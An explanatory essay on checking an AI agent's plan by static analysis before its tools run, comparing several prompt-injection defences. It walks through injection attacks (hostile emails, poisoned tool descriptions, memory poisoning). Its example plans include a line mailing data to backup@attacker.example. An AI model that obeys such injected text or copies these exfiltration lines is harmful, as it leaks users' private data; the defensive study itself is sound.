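# Checking an AI Agent's Generated Plan by Static Analysis Before Its Tools Run

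## Why an agent would write a program before it acts

In an AI agent, a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools, which are functions that read from or act on the outside world, such as one that searches a mailbox, sends a message or deletes a file. Most agents choose these actions one at a time, each after seeing the result of the last. In others, a planner, usually a language model, first writes the intended tool calls as a program, called the plan. A checker compares the plan with a policy, which is a machine-readable rule about permitted actions or data flows, and an executor runs the plan only if it passes. The method comes from compilers and program verification, where people have long had to decide whether to run code written by strangers. It appeals to agent developers because the checker can reject a plan before any of its tools run.

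### The agent loop and a hostile email

OpenAI's *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* describes the usual design, as used in the company's own coding agent, which may make hundreds of tool calls for a single request. In this design, the model either gives a final answer or requests a tool call. After each call, the surrounding software adds the tool's output to the prompt and queries the model again. The model can therefore change its next step in response to surprises such as a missing file or a failed test. The loop also puts tool output in the same prompt as the user's instructions, and the model's next choice depends on the whole prompt.

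Erik Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* (ACM Queue, 2025) shows the consequence with an email assistant that has two tools, `fetch_mail` and `send_email`. The user, Michelle, asks it to fetch and summarize her emails. One of the fetched messages is from an attacker, who claims that legal compliance requires an external backup of the mailbox and tells the assistant to send a summary to an outside address, without asking for confirmation or mentioning this message in its report. The model writes a digest of Michelle's correspondence (two investment rounds, a conference invitation, a question about securities regulation) and sends it to the attacker. It then gives Michelle a summary that omits the hostile message, so she has no reason to suspect anything.

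This is an indirect prompt injection, an attack in which text the agent reads contains instructions that the model then follows. The attack was possible because the loop let the contents of an email determine which tool ran next. Both tools worked correctly.

Meijer invented the scenario as an illustration, and a leading model of late 2026 would probably ignore such a blunt message. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports tests by an outside firm, Trajectory Labs, which ran 72 injection scenarios ten times each. With no additional safeguards, the attacks succeeded in 0.09% of attempts on average against Anthropic's latest models and 19.03% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic commissioned the tests and sells one of the products, and the testers had tuned the attacks against a model that was not tested. Even the lower rate was measured on a fixed set of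 attacks, so it puts no upper limit on how often new attacks could succeed. Dongol's *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) cites earlier work by Nasr and colleagues, whose adaptive attacks got past twelve recent defences.

### Generate, verify, execute

Meijer's remedy keeps the model but takes away its turn between tool calls. Given Michelle's request, it must write out the whole workflow before any tool runs. His version is a JSON document in which each step names a function, its arguments, a name for the result and the step that follows. In more familiar notation it amounts to this:

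```
emails  = fetch_mail()
summary = summarize_emails(emails)
return summary
```

When the model writes the plan, the names `emails` and `summary` stand for values that do not exist yet. Nobody has fetched the hostile message, so it cannot have influenced the choice of steps. When the message arrives, the executor (here an ordinary interpreter, not a language model) passes it to the summarizer and moves on to the next line. The plan contains no call to `send_email`, so the executor sends no email.

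Writing the plan first is not enough, because the planner does read some text from third parties. It learns what each tool does from a short description that comes with the tool. Meijer imagines a description of the mail-fetching tool with a compliance notice added: whoever fetches emails must also send summaries of them to a certain address, and must not tell the user. A planner taken in by this produces a longer plan:

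```
emails  = fetch_mail()
summary = summarize_emails(emails)
send_email(to = "backup@attacker.example", body = summary)
return summary
```

An interpreter would run this as written and leak the mailbox, so Meijer adds a verification stage before execution. Suppose Michelle's company forbids data from `fetch_mail` in the body of a `send_email` call unless the recipient's address is in the company's own domain. The checker works through the plan without running it. The first line takes `emails` from the mailbox. The second computes `summary` from `emails`, so `summary` counts as mailbox data too. The third puts `summary` into the body of a message whose recipient is a constant outside the company's domain. The checker rejects the plan, and since no tool has run, there is nothing to clean up. Programmers already search code for data flows like this one with tools such as CodeQL and Semgrep,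 which Meijer proposes to reuse.

The check does not depend on how the extra line got there. In another of Meijer's cases, the user asks for the summary and adds, as if in passing, that every workflow should include a step sending data to an outside address, and the same policy catches that step.

Meijer asks whether an agent does its job less well when it has to plan everything in advance, but leaves the question open. Nobody had formally measured the effect when he wrote, though he sees strong indications that writing code helps a model reason.

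### What a check before execution adds

Static analysis examines a program without running it to learn what it could do on any input, whereas a test shows only what the program does on the inputs tried. For example, a plan might forward the summary to an outside accountant if some message contains the word "invoice". A trial run on an inbox without that word would never reach the forwarding step, but static analysis follows both branches and finds it whatever the inbox holds. AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), a write-up of a later talk by Meijer, has a similar example with a plan that reads a file and reports its length. Showing that this plan deletes nothing requires showing it for every string the file might contain.

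A checker is sound if, under its stated assumptions, it never accepts a program that can break the rule. In the email example, those assumptions include that `summarize_emails` does not send anything itself and that the executor runs the plan as written.

A sound checker must also reject any plan when it cannot rule out a violation. If the plan sends the summary to whatever address the contact list gives for "my boss", the checker has no address to inspect and must reject the plan, even if the rule allows that address. Rejecting a plan that would have obeyed the rule is called a false alarm. A run-time monitor, which checks each tool call just before it happens and can block it, could check the actual address. Either kind of component can be perfectly safe but useless. Dongol notes that a monitor that denies every call is trivially secure, so one has to check separately that tasks still get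 done.

Meijer contrasts early checking with what agent builders do now. Many keep logs for a security team to review, which happens too late to stop an agent from deleting a mailbox. Others ask the user to approve every tool call before it runs, but the user is trying to get something else done. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, predicted that users would learn to click "OK" as fast as possible, and Meijer compares approval prompts to cookie banners.

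Evidence now supports that prediction. Anthropic reports that users of Claude Code, its coding agent, approve 97% of permission prompts. In a study with 1,053 paid testers, the organisers swapped one prompt in each session for a plainly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after fifty or more prompts. The testers were not working on their own code, and Anthropic published the figures to justify replacing the prompts with its own automated reviewer, so the exact rates deserve some caution. In the same data, users reject 39% of the plans the agent presents for approval. Some of those rejections must reflect disagreement about how to do the job rather than alertness to danger, but the rate suggests that people do read plans.

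Even an attentive user can end up authorizing the wrong action. Dongol describes an assistant whose user, Alice, approves each reply before it is sent. Each approval allows one call to the sending tool, with any content. If an injected call arrives just after Alice approves a reply, it sends her private data and uses up the approval, so the monitor then blocks the reply she meant to send.

Meijer's argument is weaker against monitors. He calls them reactive because, in his example, the agent has already retrieved and processed private mail by the time a monitor steps in. But Michelle asked for her mail, and a monitor that blocks the `send_email` call prevents the leak to the attacker just as rejecting the plan would. Monitors can also come with proofs. Dongol uses the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL to analyze a monitor that permanently withdraws every tool an injection could call when the agent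 first reads untrusted text. He proves that an injection then leaks nothing that the same plan would not have leaked with a model that ignores injections. The theorem covers every plan, but it assumes that each injection is a single call, that the model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance, and that the attacker sees the messages but not their timing.

A static checker examines the whole program before any tool runs, while a monitor checks only the path the run takes. By the time a monitor blocks a call, earlier calls have already happened. Suppose a plan cancels a hotel booking and then emails the traveller's passport details to a new hotel, against company policy. A monitor that blocks the email leaves the traveller without a room. A checker that finds the violation rejects the whole plan before the booking is cancelled. Meijer adds that a monitor can't enforce some policies, depending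 on the policy language and how much state the monitor keeps. He still expects real systems to check some conditions during the run, because they are hard or impossible to settle in advance.

### Rollback

One advantage Meijer claims for verification is that it eliminates the need for rollback, the undoing of steps already taken. He reasons that if only verified plans execute, no breach occurs that would need undoing. This follows from soundness for breaches of the written policy, but it is too strong as a description of agents in operation.

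Plans can fail for reasons unrelated to security. For example, a payment service may go down after the agent has booked the flight but before it has booked the hotel. The Saga pattern, which Garcia-Molina and Salem published for databases in 1987, handles such failures by pairing steps with compensating actions. *POLAR* (2026) lists several earlier agent systems that adapt the pattern, including SagaLLM, which writes the compensating actions when it builds the workflow and runs them in reverse order after a failure. A verified plan needs compensating actions too. It can satisfy the policy and still be wrong, as in Meijer's example of a request to delete two text files that becomes a command to delete every text file. The run-time checks that Meijer accepts as necessary can also leave a job partly finished, because a monitor that stops a verified plan at the fourth step does not undo the first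 three.

Another difficulty, raised by Chen, Dong and colleagues (2026) in *Cordon*, is that the evidence for a decision often appears only during the run. In their example, an agent diagnosing an outage reads application logs, summarizes the failures and prepares a message for the team's Slack channel. Every step is routine, but these logs contain a secret key, which the summary may include. Before the run, a checker can treat all logs as secret and reject a useful plan, or treat them as harmless and miss the leak. Cordon, a run-time system, postpones the decision. It makes local changes in a shadow copy, holds outgoing messages in an outbox, and releases them only after examining the task as a whole. In the team's own evaluation on 45 risky workflows, Cordon stopped all 45 violations, adaptations of existing defences stopped 14, and plain execution stopped none. Because the system's designers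 ran this evaluation, it is weak evidence of how Cordon would perform elsewhere. Even Cordon can truly roll back only local state. Once a message has left the outbox, the only options are to audit it and compensate for it.

Meijer's instinct is sound here. *CoAgent* (2026) describes a system in which every tool first saves whatever a later undo will need, such as a copy of a database before the agent drops it. But sending external mail and executing a payment cannot be undone, so the system has to mark such tools as unrecoverable. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agents with persistent memory, finds that rollback is the rarest capability among the systems it covers, and that rollback of external effects is rarer still. A check before execution is therefore most valuable for actions that cannot be rolled back, and a system with such a check still needs rollback for the rest.

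### Where the idea comes from

Little of this is new, as Meijer acknowledges. He attributes prompt injection to the same cause as SQL injection, an attack on databases in which a website pastes a visitor's input into a command. A visitor who types a fragment of SQL instead of a name can then delete a table. The fix is to keep code and data apart, as parameterised queries do, so that the database never interprets the input as a command.

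David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* that the comparison is dangerous because a language model has no boundary between instructions and data to enforce. It processes both as one sequence of tokens from which it predicts the next. He recommends safeguards outside the model that constrain what the system can do. He and Meijer disagree less than it seems, because a plan fixed in advance moves the boundary out of the model and into an interpreter, which treats the contents of `emails` as a value, as a database treats a parameter. When the plan passes that value to another model, as it does for summarizing, the boundary disappears again and David C's objection applies in full.

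Java and .NET already check untrusted programs before running them. Both platforms verify that bytecode, the intermediate form in which programs arrive, is memory-safe, uses types correctly and respects access controls. They check some other things, such as whether an array index is in range, while the program runs.

Necula's 1997 conference paper, *Proof-Carrying Code*, gives the hard part of the work to the code's producer. The party that will run the code publishes a safety policy, and the untrusted producer sends a program with a formal proof that it obeys the policy. A small validator quickly checks the proof, and the program then runs without further checks. Nobody has to trust the producer, because tampering with the program or the proof either makes validation fail or produces a different program that is also safe. Necula applied the method to network packet filters and to assembly-language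 extensions of a compiler's run-time system. A later chapter, *Safe, Untrusted Agents Using Proof-Carrying Code*, appeared in a volume on mobile agents, which are programs that travel between computers. Meijer's 2026 talk uses the idea directly, requiring a proof from the planner along with the plan. The policies do not carry over as easily. Necula's concerned matters like valid memory addresses, which can be defined exactly, but AI Engineer concedes in its write-up that no proof system can supply the meaning of a safety policy that nobody has defined.

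The idea also has a more recent origin in language-model security, where Willison proposed in 2023 to split an assistant into two models. A privileged model takes the user's requests and can use tools, while a quarantined model without tools reads untrusted text. Ordinary software, called the controller, passes data between them. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the privileged model requests the email, and the controller stores it as `$VAR1`. The privileged model then asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller gives the actual text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`. The privileged model tells the controller to display `$VAR2` without ever having read the email or the summary. Willison thought this solution was "pretty bad", mainly because it is complicated to build and a single mistake that lets untrusted text through makes it unsafe.

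*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) lists this dual-model pattern as one of six. In another, plan-then-execute, the model fixes its list of tool calls before it sees any untrusted data. In the paper's example, a request to send today's schedule to one's boss becomes a calendar read followed by an email to a fixed address. A hostile calendar entry cannot add a call or change the recipient, but it can rewrite the body of the email. In code-then-execute, the model writes a program instead of a list, and the program can also call quarantined models to process text.

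The remaining patterns are narrower. An action selector picks actions from a menu and never sees their results. In map-reduce, an isolated model reads each document and returns something as small as a yes or no. Context minimisation deletes the user's prompt before the model composes its reply. All six patterns deliberately give up generality, because Beurer-Kellner and colleagues doubt that an agent free to attempt any task can offer reliable guarantees with current models. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (2025), a guide for developers, combines this approach with the older one by having the system verify the plan against static policies and then keep it fixed during execution.

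### Isolating the planner and checking the plan

These designs use two separate protections. They isolate the planner from untrusted text until the plan is complete, which protects the plan from hostile text. They also check the plan, which limits the damage if the planner is compromised or mistaken.

Isolation is enough to protect against the email in Michelle's inbox, and the three-line plan would have been safe without a checker. But isolation does not protect against the poisoned tool description, because the planner reads the hostile text. Nor does it protect against hostile text that users paste into their own requests, a weakness Willison acknowledged from the start. Dongol's theorems assume a trusted planner and leave both its errors and poisoned tools out of scope, so they do not establish whether the plan was good.

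If a plan is checked but the planner isn't isolated from hostile text, an attacker can use that text to ask for anything the policy permits. For example, a rule that only forbids sending mail outside the company would allow a plan that forwards Michelle's correspondence to a colleague who shouldn't see it.

Neither protection covers the text that passes through a sound plan. The hostile email still goes to the summarizer, which is a language model and may leave things out or repeat a lie. For that step, Meijer relies on conventional guardrails and a prompt that asks the summarizer to mark suspicious messages, even though the failures of such defences led him to propose verification.

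## Keeping untrusted text away from the planner

Anyone who can write text that the planner reads can influence the plan. A planner usually reads five kinds of text: the user's request, the names of the installed tools, the tools' descriptions, the outputs of tools that have already run, and earlier conversation. Isolating the planner means deciding which of these it may still read, based on who can write each one.

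### What reaches the planner

Anyone who controls the user's request also controls the plan. The systems discussed here all treat the request as trusted, because the agent is supposed to do what the user wants. The accepted risk is that the request may include text the user pasted from someone else.

A tool's publisher writes its name and description. *IsolateGPT* (Wu, Roesner and colleagues, 2024) describes agents that load tools' descriptions into the model's context, so a publisher's text can reach the planner even when a request has nothing to do with the tool. A publisher can do little with a name except imitate a better-known tool, but can use a description to ask the planner to drop a competitor, add a call or change an argument. Dongol models two attacks of this kind that the security company Invariant Labs reported in 2025. In one, a malicious tool's description contains an instruction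 to pass that tool the user's SSH key, a login credential, in a hidden argument. In the other, the description contains an instruction to send the user's mail to the attacker through a different, trusted tool, so the attack can work without the malicious tool ever running.

Anyone who can put text into a mailbox, a web page or a shared file can get text into a tool's output. The hostile message in Michelle's inbox worked at once, but *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, 2024) describes two delayed attacks. In the first, a user asks the agent to append a downloaded file of medical studies to her clinical notes and send the result to a doctor. The agent can merge the files without reading them, so the attack takes effect only when it opens the merged file, where an instruction from the download redirects the patient data. In the second, a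 hostile report contains an instruction that applies only if the agent is about to delete a file. The agent emails the report as asked, but then deletes everything in the folder instead of only the report.

Earlier conversation can contain the user's private data and text from tools that ran days ago. In SpAIware, an attack on ChatGPT that Johann Rehberger published in 2024, a web page the user asks about makes ChatGPT save an instruction to its long-term memory. ChatGPT loads that memory in every later conversation and adds to each answer an image whose web address carries the user's messages to the attacker. Keeping web pages away from the planner therefore does not help if the planner reads memories saved from earlier web pages.

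### Weak and strong attackers

*ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, Northeastern University, 2025) assumes that the attacker controls one or more of the tools installed on the user's system. It defines two threat models. In the weak one, each tool's description and schema (the formal statement of its inputs and outputs) can be trusted, so the attacker controls only what the tool does and returns. In the strong one, the attacker also writes the description and schema. The weak model is a reasonable fit for an honest company's mail reader, which relays whatever strangers send. The strong model fits a marketplace where anyone can publish a tool.

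The attacker may try to change the plan, for instance so that it leaves out a competitor's tool. The attacker may also try to corrupt the run's results, make the run fail although working tools are available, or leak the user's data. Li and colleagues leave aside attacks that prevent planning altogether, because the user would notice them.

### f-Secure: a planner that reads only trusted data

f-Secure, which Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao built at the University of Wisconsin–Madison in 2024, defends against the weak attacker. It divides the agent into a planner that reads only trusted information, a rule-based executor that may handle anything, and a security monitor between them. Asked to summarize `test.doc`, the planner first writes a step that reads the file. The executor runs this step, and the monitor stores the text under the reference `{Data_output:1}`. If the planner tries to look up the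 reference, the monitor refuses, because the file is untrusted. The planner can still write the reference into its next step, and the executor then gives the text to a fresh model instance, which produces the summary. This resembles Willison's pair of privileged and quarantined models, with an explicit rule for what the privileged one may see.

The rule uses labels, which here record how trustworthy each piece of data is. Data from the user or the system's own components counts as trusted, and outside data counts as untrusted unless the user has decided otherwise, for instance by trusting mail from colleagues. Data computed from several sources takes the label of the least trustworthy one, so the merged file of clinical notes and downloaded studies is untrusted. The monitor applies the labels to each item separately. In one example, the user wants the agent to read emails about company budgets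 and notify the manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. The search returns two messages from colleagues and one from an attacker. The planner can read the colleagues' messages and decide whether to notify the manager, but it never receives the attacker's.

Wu and colleagues state their guarantee in terms of probabilities, because a model may plan the same request differently on different occasions. Let `q` be the request and `π` a sequence of steps, and let `Q1` and `Q2` be two versions of all the information the agent could reach. The guarantee is:

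```
if Q1 and Q2 contain the same trusted information,
then Pr[π | q, Q1] = Pr[π | q, Q2]
```

The paper proves that an attacker cannot make any sequence of steps in f-Secure more or less likely, even by rewriting every untrusted email and web page. The proof covers the steps but not the data they handle, so an attacker can still get a false statement into the summary.

The guarantee also depends on tool descriptions being safe, because f-Secure labels them as trusted. A poisoned description can therefore reach the planner, and the theorem does not rule out its effects. There is another gap when a step fails. f-Secure then has the planner generate a new step, so an attacker whose text makes a tool crash could change the plan even if that text never reaches the planner. The paper excludes attacks on availability, which presumably covers this case, but then the guarantee is weaker than the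 formula suggests. In their comparison of the systems, Li and colleagues nevertheless credit f-Secure with protecting availability against the weak attacker.

f-Secure writes each step only after it has run the one before. No complete plan exists before the first tool call, so a static checker would have nothing to analyse.

### Three attacks on IsolateGPT

IsolateGPT, developed at Washington University in St. Louis and the University of Washington, focuses more on malicious tools. It runs each tool in its own compartment with its own model instance, much as browsers and phones isolate apps, and a central hub passes requests between compartments with the user's permission. In its developers' tests, IsolateGPT did everything that an unisolated system did, and it took less than 30% longer for about three quarters of the queries.

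The weakness is in the hub. Its planner writes a detailed plan from the request and the tool descriptions, but the hub keeps only the plan's list of tools. A second model, the execution manager, chooses each next tool from that list after reading the previous tool's output. Each tool has its own compartment, but all their outputs go into the execution manager's context. The f-Secure team had already exploited this in 2024. They ran the budget example against SecGPT, an earlier name for IsolateGPT, and the agent sent the budgets to the attacker.

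Li and colleagues demonstrated three further attacks using a task from the IsolateGPT paper. The agent compares the fares of two ride-hailing services, one of which they made malicious.

Their first attack stops the run. The malicious tool returns a warning that all fare-calculating apps are compromised. The execution manager treats the warning as true, quits before calling the legitimate tool, and tells the user that there was a technical problem. This works because the model that decides whether to continue reads the tools' output.

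The second attack gives the user a false fare for the competitor. The malicious tool's output contains an instruction to report its own fare correctly and inflate the other service's, and the execution manager follows it. The honest tool ran in its own compartment and returned the correct fare, but isolating it didn't help because a single model read both outputs and wrote the answer. The IsolateGPT paper had given almost the same scenario as a reason to isolate tools.

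In the third attack, the malicious tool's description contains an instruction to leave the competitor out of any fare comparison. The planner reads all the descriptions together and follows the instruction, so the user sees a single fare, with no sign that another tool was available. Keeping tool outputs away from the planner, as f-Secure does, would not have prevented this.

Li and colleagues show a worked example of each attack but give no success rates. The examples prove that the attacks can work, though they might work less often against a more robust model.

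### Planning with invented tools

ACE, short for Abstract-Concrete-Execute, removes tool descriptions from the planner's input. Its abstract planner receives only the user's request, with no list of installed tools, so it plans with tools that it makes up.

Suppose the user asks the agent to load `file.txt` and summarize it. A model first invents the tools it would need and gives each a name, a description, and typed inputs and outputs. For this request it invents `DocumentLoader`, which takes a filename and returns text, and `TextSummarizer`, which takes text and returns text. A second prompt turns the request and the invented tools into a program in a restricted form of Python. Without its type annotations, the core of the program is:

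```
doc = DocumentLoader(filename="file.txt")
res = TextSummarizer(text=doc)
display(res)
```

Neither tool exists yet. The program fixes which calls happen, their order, and what data passes between them. The publisher of an installed tool has had no chance to influence these choices.

A concrete planner then looks for installed tools that can fill the two roles. It first compares embeddings, which are lists of numbers that represent a text's meaning, and discards installed tools whose descriptions are too different from those of the invented tools. For each remaining pair of an invented and an installed tool, it asks a model whether the installed tool can do the job. If so, the model also writes adapter code to convert arguments and results between the two tools' formats.

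The model judges each pair separately. When it considers a malicious summarizer, the honest one's description is not in its context, so an instruction to exclude the honest one has no effect. A plan can also specify every installed tool that fits a role, so ACE can call both services in the fare comparison, whatever one publisher has written about the other.

Publishers can still use a description to get their own tools accepted. The matching prompt instructs the model to match tools if at all possible and to reject only those with completely different purposes. This avoids rejecting useful tools, but it also makes hostile ones more likely to be accepted. An attacker might also influence the adapter code, since the model writes it after reading the description. If that code runs in confinement, the attacker gains little, because the code handles only data going to or from a tool the attacker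 already controls.

Often several installed tools fit, so ACE must choose between concrete plans. It combines the privileges that each plan's tools need, such as file or network access, and ranks one plan above another only if its set of privileges is a strict subset of the other's. For example, suppose one document loader needs file access, another needs both file and network access, and the summarizer needs neither. The plan with the first loader needs {files} and the plan with the second needs {files, network}, so ACE chooses the first plan. When this rule doesn't settle the choice, ACE picks at random.

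This rule ignores which tool holds which privilege. If the summarizer needs the network to call an online service, both plans need {files, network}. ACE may then pick the loader that can both read the user's files and send them elsewhere. Publishers also declare the privileges their tools need, so a malicious publisher can get its summarizer chosen by declaring few. That summarizer would still receive the user's document and could return a false summary without any privileges. Li and colleagues call the rule an initial approach and suggest that later versions could favour tools from trusted providers.

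After matching the tools, ACE analyses the data flows in the plan. It then runs the plan, with each tool in an isolated worker.

### The InjecAgent evaluation

Li and colleagues tested ACE on InjecAgent, a benchmark with 17 tools that a user might want and 52 that an attacker wants the agent to call. In each of its 1,054 cases, the user's request leads the agent to a tool whose output contains an injected instruction. The instruction is meant to harm the user directly in 510 cases and to steal data in 544. The attack succeeds if the agent calls one of the attacker's tools. ACE called none of them, whichever models it used.

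ACE's usefulness varied with the models used. A case counts as a success if ACE matches the right installed tool and runs it without an error.

| Models, with release dates | Matched the right tool | Ran without error, if matched | Overall |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o (May 2024) | 55.3% | 85.4% | 47.2% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet (February 2025) | 81.3% | 82.1% | 66.7% |
| Qwen 2.5 72B (September 2024) | 79.5% | 85.3% | 67.8% |
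| GPT-4o for the abstract plan, o3-mini (January 2025) for matching | 82.1% | 91.7% | 75.2% |

GPT-4o wrote the abstract plans in both the first row and the last. Replacing it with o3-mini for the matching alone raised the share of correct matches from 55.3% to 82.1%, so GPT-4o's main weakness was recognising suitable tools. All these models are well over a year old, so 75.2% may not be the most that ACE could achieve with current ones.

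The perfect security score follows from ACE's design and does not depend on the models. ACE fixes the plan before any tool runs. It then treats every tool output as a value of a declared type, such as a number or a string, and never puts it into the context of the models that plan and match. An instruction inside an output therefore cannot lead those models to call another tool. If an installed summarizer is a language model, it still reads the document, but ACE treats its answer only as a string.

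The 1,054 cases therefore test whether the code follows the design, and more of the same kind would add little. An agent that never called a tool would also score 100%. InjecAgent does not count a false fare or a misleading summary as a successful attack. It also does not test hostile descriptions, because its injected instructions arrive in tool outputs. The evidence on hostile descriptions is that ACE resisted the description attack that had worked on IsolateGPT, together with the argument that matching each pair separately prevents such attacks.

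In exchange, ACE gives up most of what a model usually does with a tool's output. Its models cannot choose the next step based on a result, rephrase the result or detect that it makes no sense. The abstract planner also has no access to the installed tools' descriptions. Li and colleagues describe a user who asked ACE to "find my future flight". The abstract planner invented a tool that searches for flights by origin, destination and date. The installed tool searched existing reservations, which is probably what the user meant, but the matching model did not match the two descriptions, so the request failed. An ordinary planner could have resolved the ambiguity by reading the installed tool's description, but ACE's users have to resolve it themselves by giving more detail in the request.

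In another case, the user wanted details of a file stored in Dropbox, and ACE found the right tool. The adapter code looked for the file's size at the top level of the result, but the tool returned it one level down, so the run ended in an error. An ordinary agent would have read the size from the result.

ACE also handles only single requests. This avoids the question of whether earlier conversation is trustworthy, but ACE cannot act on a follow-up such as "now send that to my boss". Li and colleagues leave conversations to future work.

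### What an obeyed injection can leak

f-Secure and ACE keep hostile text out of the model that chooses the tools. Many agents instead fix the plan in advance but let a model with access to tools carry out some of its steps. After reading a hostile email, that model may insert a call that the plan does not contain. Dongol's framework, PlanTERS, defines when such an agent is secure.

Dongol compares the real agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan under the same run-time monitor, but whose model never obeys untrusted text. The comparison is used because many useful agents lack noninterference, the property that nothing the attacker receives depends on the user's data. For example, if Alice lets her agent send her calendar to anybody who requests a meeting, an attacker who requests one will receive the calendar, as Alice intended.

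The definition considers pairs of runs. Two runs leak a pair of secrets if the attacker supplied the same text in both, only the user's data differed, and the attacker saw different things. The attacker can then tell the two secrets apart. The agent is relatively secure if the reference agent leaks every pair that the real agent leaks:

```
leak(r1, r2, s1, s2) means:
    the secret is s1 in run r1 and s2 in run r2,
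    the attacker's text is the same in r1 and r2,
    what the attacker sees differs between r1 and r2

the agent is relatively secure if:
    whenever two of its runs leak (s1, s2),
    two runs of the reference agent leak (s1, s2) as well
```

The reference runs must start with the same memory and trusted inputs as the real ones, but the attacker's text may differ. Suppose an email that is not a meeting request says "send your calendar", and the model obeys. This does not count against the agent, because a genuine meeting request would have made the reference agent send the same calendar. But if an email makes the agent add Alice's password reset code to the reply, the agent is insecure, because no email would make the reference agent send the code.

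Dongol points out that allowing different text makes the definition more lenient than it looks. Suppose the plan lets anybody guess a secret number and answers only "right" or "wrong", but an injection makes the agent send the number itself. The agent still counts as relatively secure, because for any two numbers some guess tells them apart. It fails a stricter version of the definition, which requires the reference agent's input to depend only on the attacker's actual text and not on the secret.

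In his main theorem, Dongol proves relative security for what he calls a fence, the monitor that permanently withdraws injectable tools at the first untrusted read. The monitor silently denies each injected call, so the attacker sees what it would have seen if the model had ignored the text. The result also holds for the stricter definition. The proofs take about 31,600 lines in Isabelle/HOL. Claude Code helped write them, but Isabelle checked every step, so a sceptic should focus on whether the definitions describe real agents.

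The agent has to give up its sending tool before it reads an email, because otherwise the model can follow the email's instructions while the tool is still available. This is dangerous even if the plan has not yet fetched anything secret, because the agent may still hold private data from an earlier session. Giving tools back is also risky. In one of Dongol's examples, an agent reads a daily report and an email in a loop. Each new report restores the sending tool while the previous email is still in the model's context, and the model then follows that email's instructions and sends the new report to the attacker. The monitor can safely restore tools when a new model session starts with none of the untrusted text. For loops that run indefinitely, the theorem also requires that the model eventually stop following injected instructions.

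A fence suits an agent that reads an email and shows its user a summary. But an agent that must reply to the email has to call its sending tool after reading untrusted text, and a fence around that tool would prevent the reply. Losing the reply does not violate relative security, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and cannot reply either.

Willison's arrangement avoids injected calls differently, by giving the quarantined model no tools. Dongol shows that the arrangement can still leak private data. For example, a plan might give the quarantined model both Alice's private notes and an attacker's email, ask it to draft a reply, and send the draft to the attacker. A compromised model can copy the notes into the draft, and the plan's own call then sends them to the attacker.

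The fence theorem does not cover several realistic attacks. Deleting a whole folder leaks nothing, so it falls outside the definition, although f-Secure's guarantee covers it if the instruction arrives in untrusted text. The theorem also excludes tools whose answers depend on the query, such as a search engine that the attacker runs, because the attacker could read the user's data in the query and tailor the reply. It also excludes models whose decision to obey depends on the secrets or on the monitor's responses. Real models do react to such responses, for example by trying something else after a refusal.

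The limit to single-call injections matters too, because an injected program could overwrite a variable that the plan is about to send without making a call that the fence could deny. Dongol proves that a fence still works against injected programs if they run in a sandbox that discards their changes and if the fence covers reads as well as calls. SpAIware breaks a different assumption, that a fresh session starts without hostile text. To stop it, the monitor must treat loading saved memory as an untrusted read.

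In an appendix, Dongol shows that a fence can also stop a version of the poisoned-description attack in which the plan is fixed before the agent reads the descriptions. In the reported attacks, however, the model that read the descriptions also chose the calls, so a fence offers no guarantee because the harmful call may be part of the plan itself. To defend against these attacks, a designer can either hide the descriptions from the planner, as ACE does, or let the planner read them and check the plan it writes.

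## Plan languages that a checker can analyse

How much a checker can establish about a plan depends largely on the language the planner writes it in. If the plan is a list of ten tool calls, the checker can determine exactly which tools will run and in what order, but if it is a long program in ordinary Python, the checker may not even be able to identify the tools.

### Rice's theorem

In 1953 the logician Henry Gordon Rice published a theorem that limits what a checker can determine about plans written in a general-purpose programming language. If some programs behave in a certain way and others don't, no algorithm can correctly decide, for every program, whether it behaves that way. For example, no checker can decide for every plan whether it sends mail outside the company. The theorem doesn't apply to properties of a program's text, such as whether it contains the word `send_email`, which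 a text search can determine.

The proof builds on Alan Turing's result of 1936 that no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether it ever finishes. Consider a plan whose first line does some calculation and sends no mail:

```
some_calculation()
send_email(to="backup@attacker.example", body=summary)
```

The plan leaks the summary if and only if the calculation finishes. A checker that was right about every plan of this form could therefore also decide whether any given calculation finishes, which Turing ruled out. Hard cases can be very short:

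```
n = 4
while is_sum_of_two_primes(n):
    n = n + 2
send_email(to="backup@attacker.example", body=summary)
```

The loop ends only if some even number greater than 2 is not the sum of two primes. To decide whether this plan can send the email, a checker would have to settle Goldbach's conjecture, which has been unsolved since 1742.

A designer can restrict the language so that planners cannot write such programs, accept a checker that rejects some safe plans, or let the checker return "unknown". If the agent rejects an "unknown" plan, it may be rejecting a safe one. If it runs the plan anyway, the check is no longer sound. It can also ask the user or leave the decision to a run-time monitor, but both options have weaknesses.

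Removing loops does not make exact answers possible either. Suppose a plan takes a list of whole numbers from a tool and sends an email only if they solve a certain polynomial equation, possibly with many unknowns. In 1970 Yuri Matiyasevich completed the proof that no algorithm can decide, for every polynomial equation with whole-number coefficients, whether it has a whole-number solution. So no checker can always tell whether the condition of a single `if` can be true. Practical checkers assume that either branch may run. This is quick and sound, but it makes them reject some plans because of branches that could never run.

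### Where ordinary Python defeats the checker

That approach works only if the checker can find the branches and the calls, and several features of Python hide them. The most drastic is code built from strings:

```
note = fetch_mail()[0].body
exec(note)
```

`exec` runs a string as Python code. If a plan passes the text of an email to `exec`, that part of the program does not exist until the email arrives, so a checker cannot analyse it beforehand. The sender of the email can also write part of the plan, which undoes any isolation of the planner.

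Reflection lets a program look up its own parts by name:

```
action = getattr(tools, name)
action(summary)
```

If `name` comes from a file, `action` could be any function in `tools`. A sound checker must allow for the most harmful one, so it will reject almost every plan that contains these lines.

A plan can also choose a call's target at run time without reflection:

```
actions = {"save": save_file, "send": send_email}
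action = actions[choice]
action(summary)
```

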